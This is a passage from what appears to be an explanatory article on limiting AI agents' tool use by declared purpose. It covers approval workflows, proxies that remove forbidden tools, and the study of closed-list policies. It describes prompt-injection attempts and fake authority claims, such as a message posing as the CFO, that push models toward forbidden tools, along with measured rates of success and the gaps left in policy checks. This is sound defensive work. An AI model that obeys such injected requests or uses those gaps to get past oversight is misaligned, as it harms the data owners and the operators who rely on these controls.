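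In the second run, the session had a declared intent that a person had approved. Each tool had one of three verdicts, so the agent could read, had to ask before updating the dashboard, and could not grant access. The policy blocked the grant, a person approved the dashboard update, and the task finished. The agent could draft the intent, but the draft took effect only if a person approved it. The agent also had no tool for removing a policy, and adding one couldn't override an existing denial.

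This is only one attack on one task, and it is easy for the policy to block because a quality check never needs the grant tool. Similar rules that allow or block whole tools would stop request B but miss request C, which uses a permitted tool on the wrong queue. Sinha and Zaharia also say that the intent doesn't control what passes through permitted actions. If the note had asked the agent to copy customers' details into the dashboard summary, only the person approving the update could have noticed.

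### Why the rule can't live in the prompt

It would be simpler to write the permitted purpose into the agent's instructions. *Prompts Don't Protect* (Uppala, 2026) tested this on 200 tasks designed to lead a model to use a forbidden tool. For example, an analytics agent might receive a message from someone claiming to be the CFO and asking for an urgent refund, when the refund tool belongs to the payments department. The model's tool list contained between 71 and 182 tools. The test compared three conditions: no guidance, instructions that listed the permitted tools and forbade the rest, and a proxy that removed the forbidden tools.

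| Model | No guidance | Rule in the prompt | Tools removed by a proxy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66.0% | 4.0% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 68.5% | 11.5% | 0% |
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 48.5% | 37.0% | 0% |

The figures give the share of tasks in which the model chose a forbidden tool. Claims of authority were especially persuasive. In tasks that contained such a claim, Haiku chose a forbidden tool 96% of the time without guidance and still did so 22% of the time when given the rule. These claims don't affect a proxy, because it takes the agent's role from a token.

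The zeros follow from the design, because a model can't choose a tool that isn't on its list. A model can still invent or copy a tool's name, so Uppala's proxy checks the permission again at each call. The percentages for prompts come from three small models, and the test forced them to choose a tool, which probably made the results look worse. In a separate experiment, Uppala gave the models 100 requests that no permitted tool could satisfy and let them decline. With only the rule in the prompt, Haiku made no call in 99% of cases.

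In the same experiment, Llama still called a permitted tool that couldn't do the job in 71% of those 100 requests after the forbidden tools were removed, and made no call in the other 29%. On 140 legitimate requests, the proxy never refused a permitted call. But Llama's success rate rose from 77.9% with the prompt rule to 82.1% with the proxy, while Qwen's fell from 60.7% to 48.6%, which Uppala attributes to the different set of tools each model could see.

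### Work that no list foresaw

A closed list can block legitimate work. For example, a faulty product could lead to refunds both to customers and from suppliers, and a manager might reasonably want one summary of the two. No entry on the list covers that summary, so the gateway refuses a request that a sensible colleague would have allowed.

A company can find many of these gaps before they affect anyone by testing new rules first. AWS recommends logging the rules' decisions without enforcing them, then switching to enforcement once the decisions look right. For rare cases, the gateway can ask for approval instead of refusing the request. Adding an entry called "general support work" would close the gaps only by removing the restriction. In Byun and colleagues' scheme, it corresponds to allowing the purpose at the top of the tree and prohibiting nothing, so every access complies.

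Even a careful addition to a policy can block intended work and permit something nobody wanted. *Agenra* gives the example of a task that may delete records A and B once each. The monitor goes through the permissions in order, first one deletion of B and then one of A. If someone widens the first permission to cover either record, deleting A can use it up, which leaves no permission for B and lets the agent delete A again. *Agenra*'s checks were tested on 51 policy changes written by its researchers. They approved all 21 that kept every existing workflow running and none of the 30 that broke one. A change that passes can still be unsafe. For example, raising the limit on how often an agent may send a report keeps every workflow running but also permits a second send.

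Denying everything not on the list blocks forgotten tools and queues, but it can't prevent harm done with permitted ones unless someone writes a rule against it. In another of *Agenra*'s examples, an agent is allowed to send Alice the public parts of a private report. A rule that only public text may be sent still lets the agent send her unrelated public text. Requiring the text to come from the step that removes private fields isn't enough either, because the agent can put an attacker's text through that step. Preventing this took a further rule on where the step's input comes from. Similarly, the rule for refund summaries doesn't stop the agent from including a customer's bank details.

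It also doesn't control what happens to the summary afterwards. Zhu and Wang say the same of their certificates, which limit what the agent may do for one request but don't prove that every later use of the data fits a privacy purpose. A colleague could paste the summary into a marketing plan the next day, and the gateway would have no request to check.

### Which sources may change a decision

A source widens access if it can permit something the agent couldn't otherwise do in the current session, and narrows access if it can only remove permissions. The difference depends mostly on who can write the purpose and what supports it.

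| Source of the purpose | Permitted use | Why |
|---|---|---|
| Model's free text | Log it; a conflict or an admitted doubt may trigger review | The model can write any text without changing what the request does |
| Model's choice from a list | Only narrow, within the purposes already open for the session | A manipulated model can pick the most permissive label, so its choice must not add permissions |
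| Certificate from the user's message | Only narrow; an uncertain interpretation triggers a question or review | Text in the tickets can't reach it, but the gateway may have misread the user |
| Application workflow | Narrow, or widen up to a limit that an administrator has set for that step | The application records what the user selected, and the model can't alter that record |
| Signed human approval | Widen for one exact action, within what the approver may grant | An accountable person has seen the action and its target, and the agent can't produce the signature |
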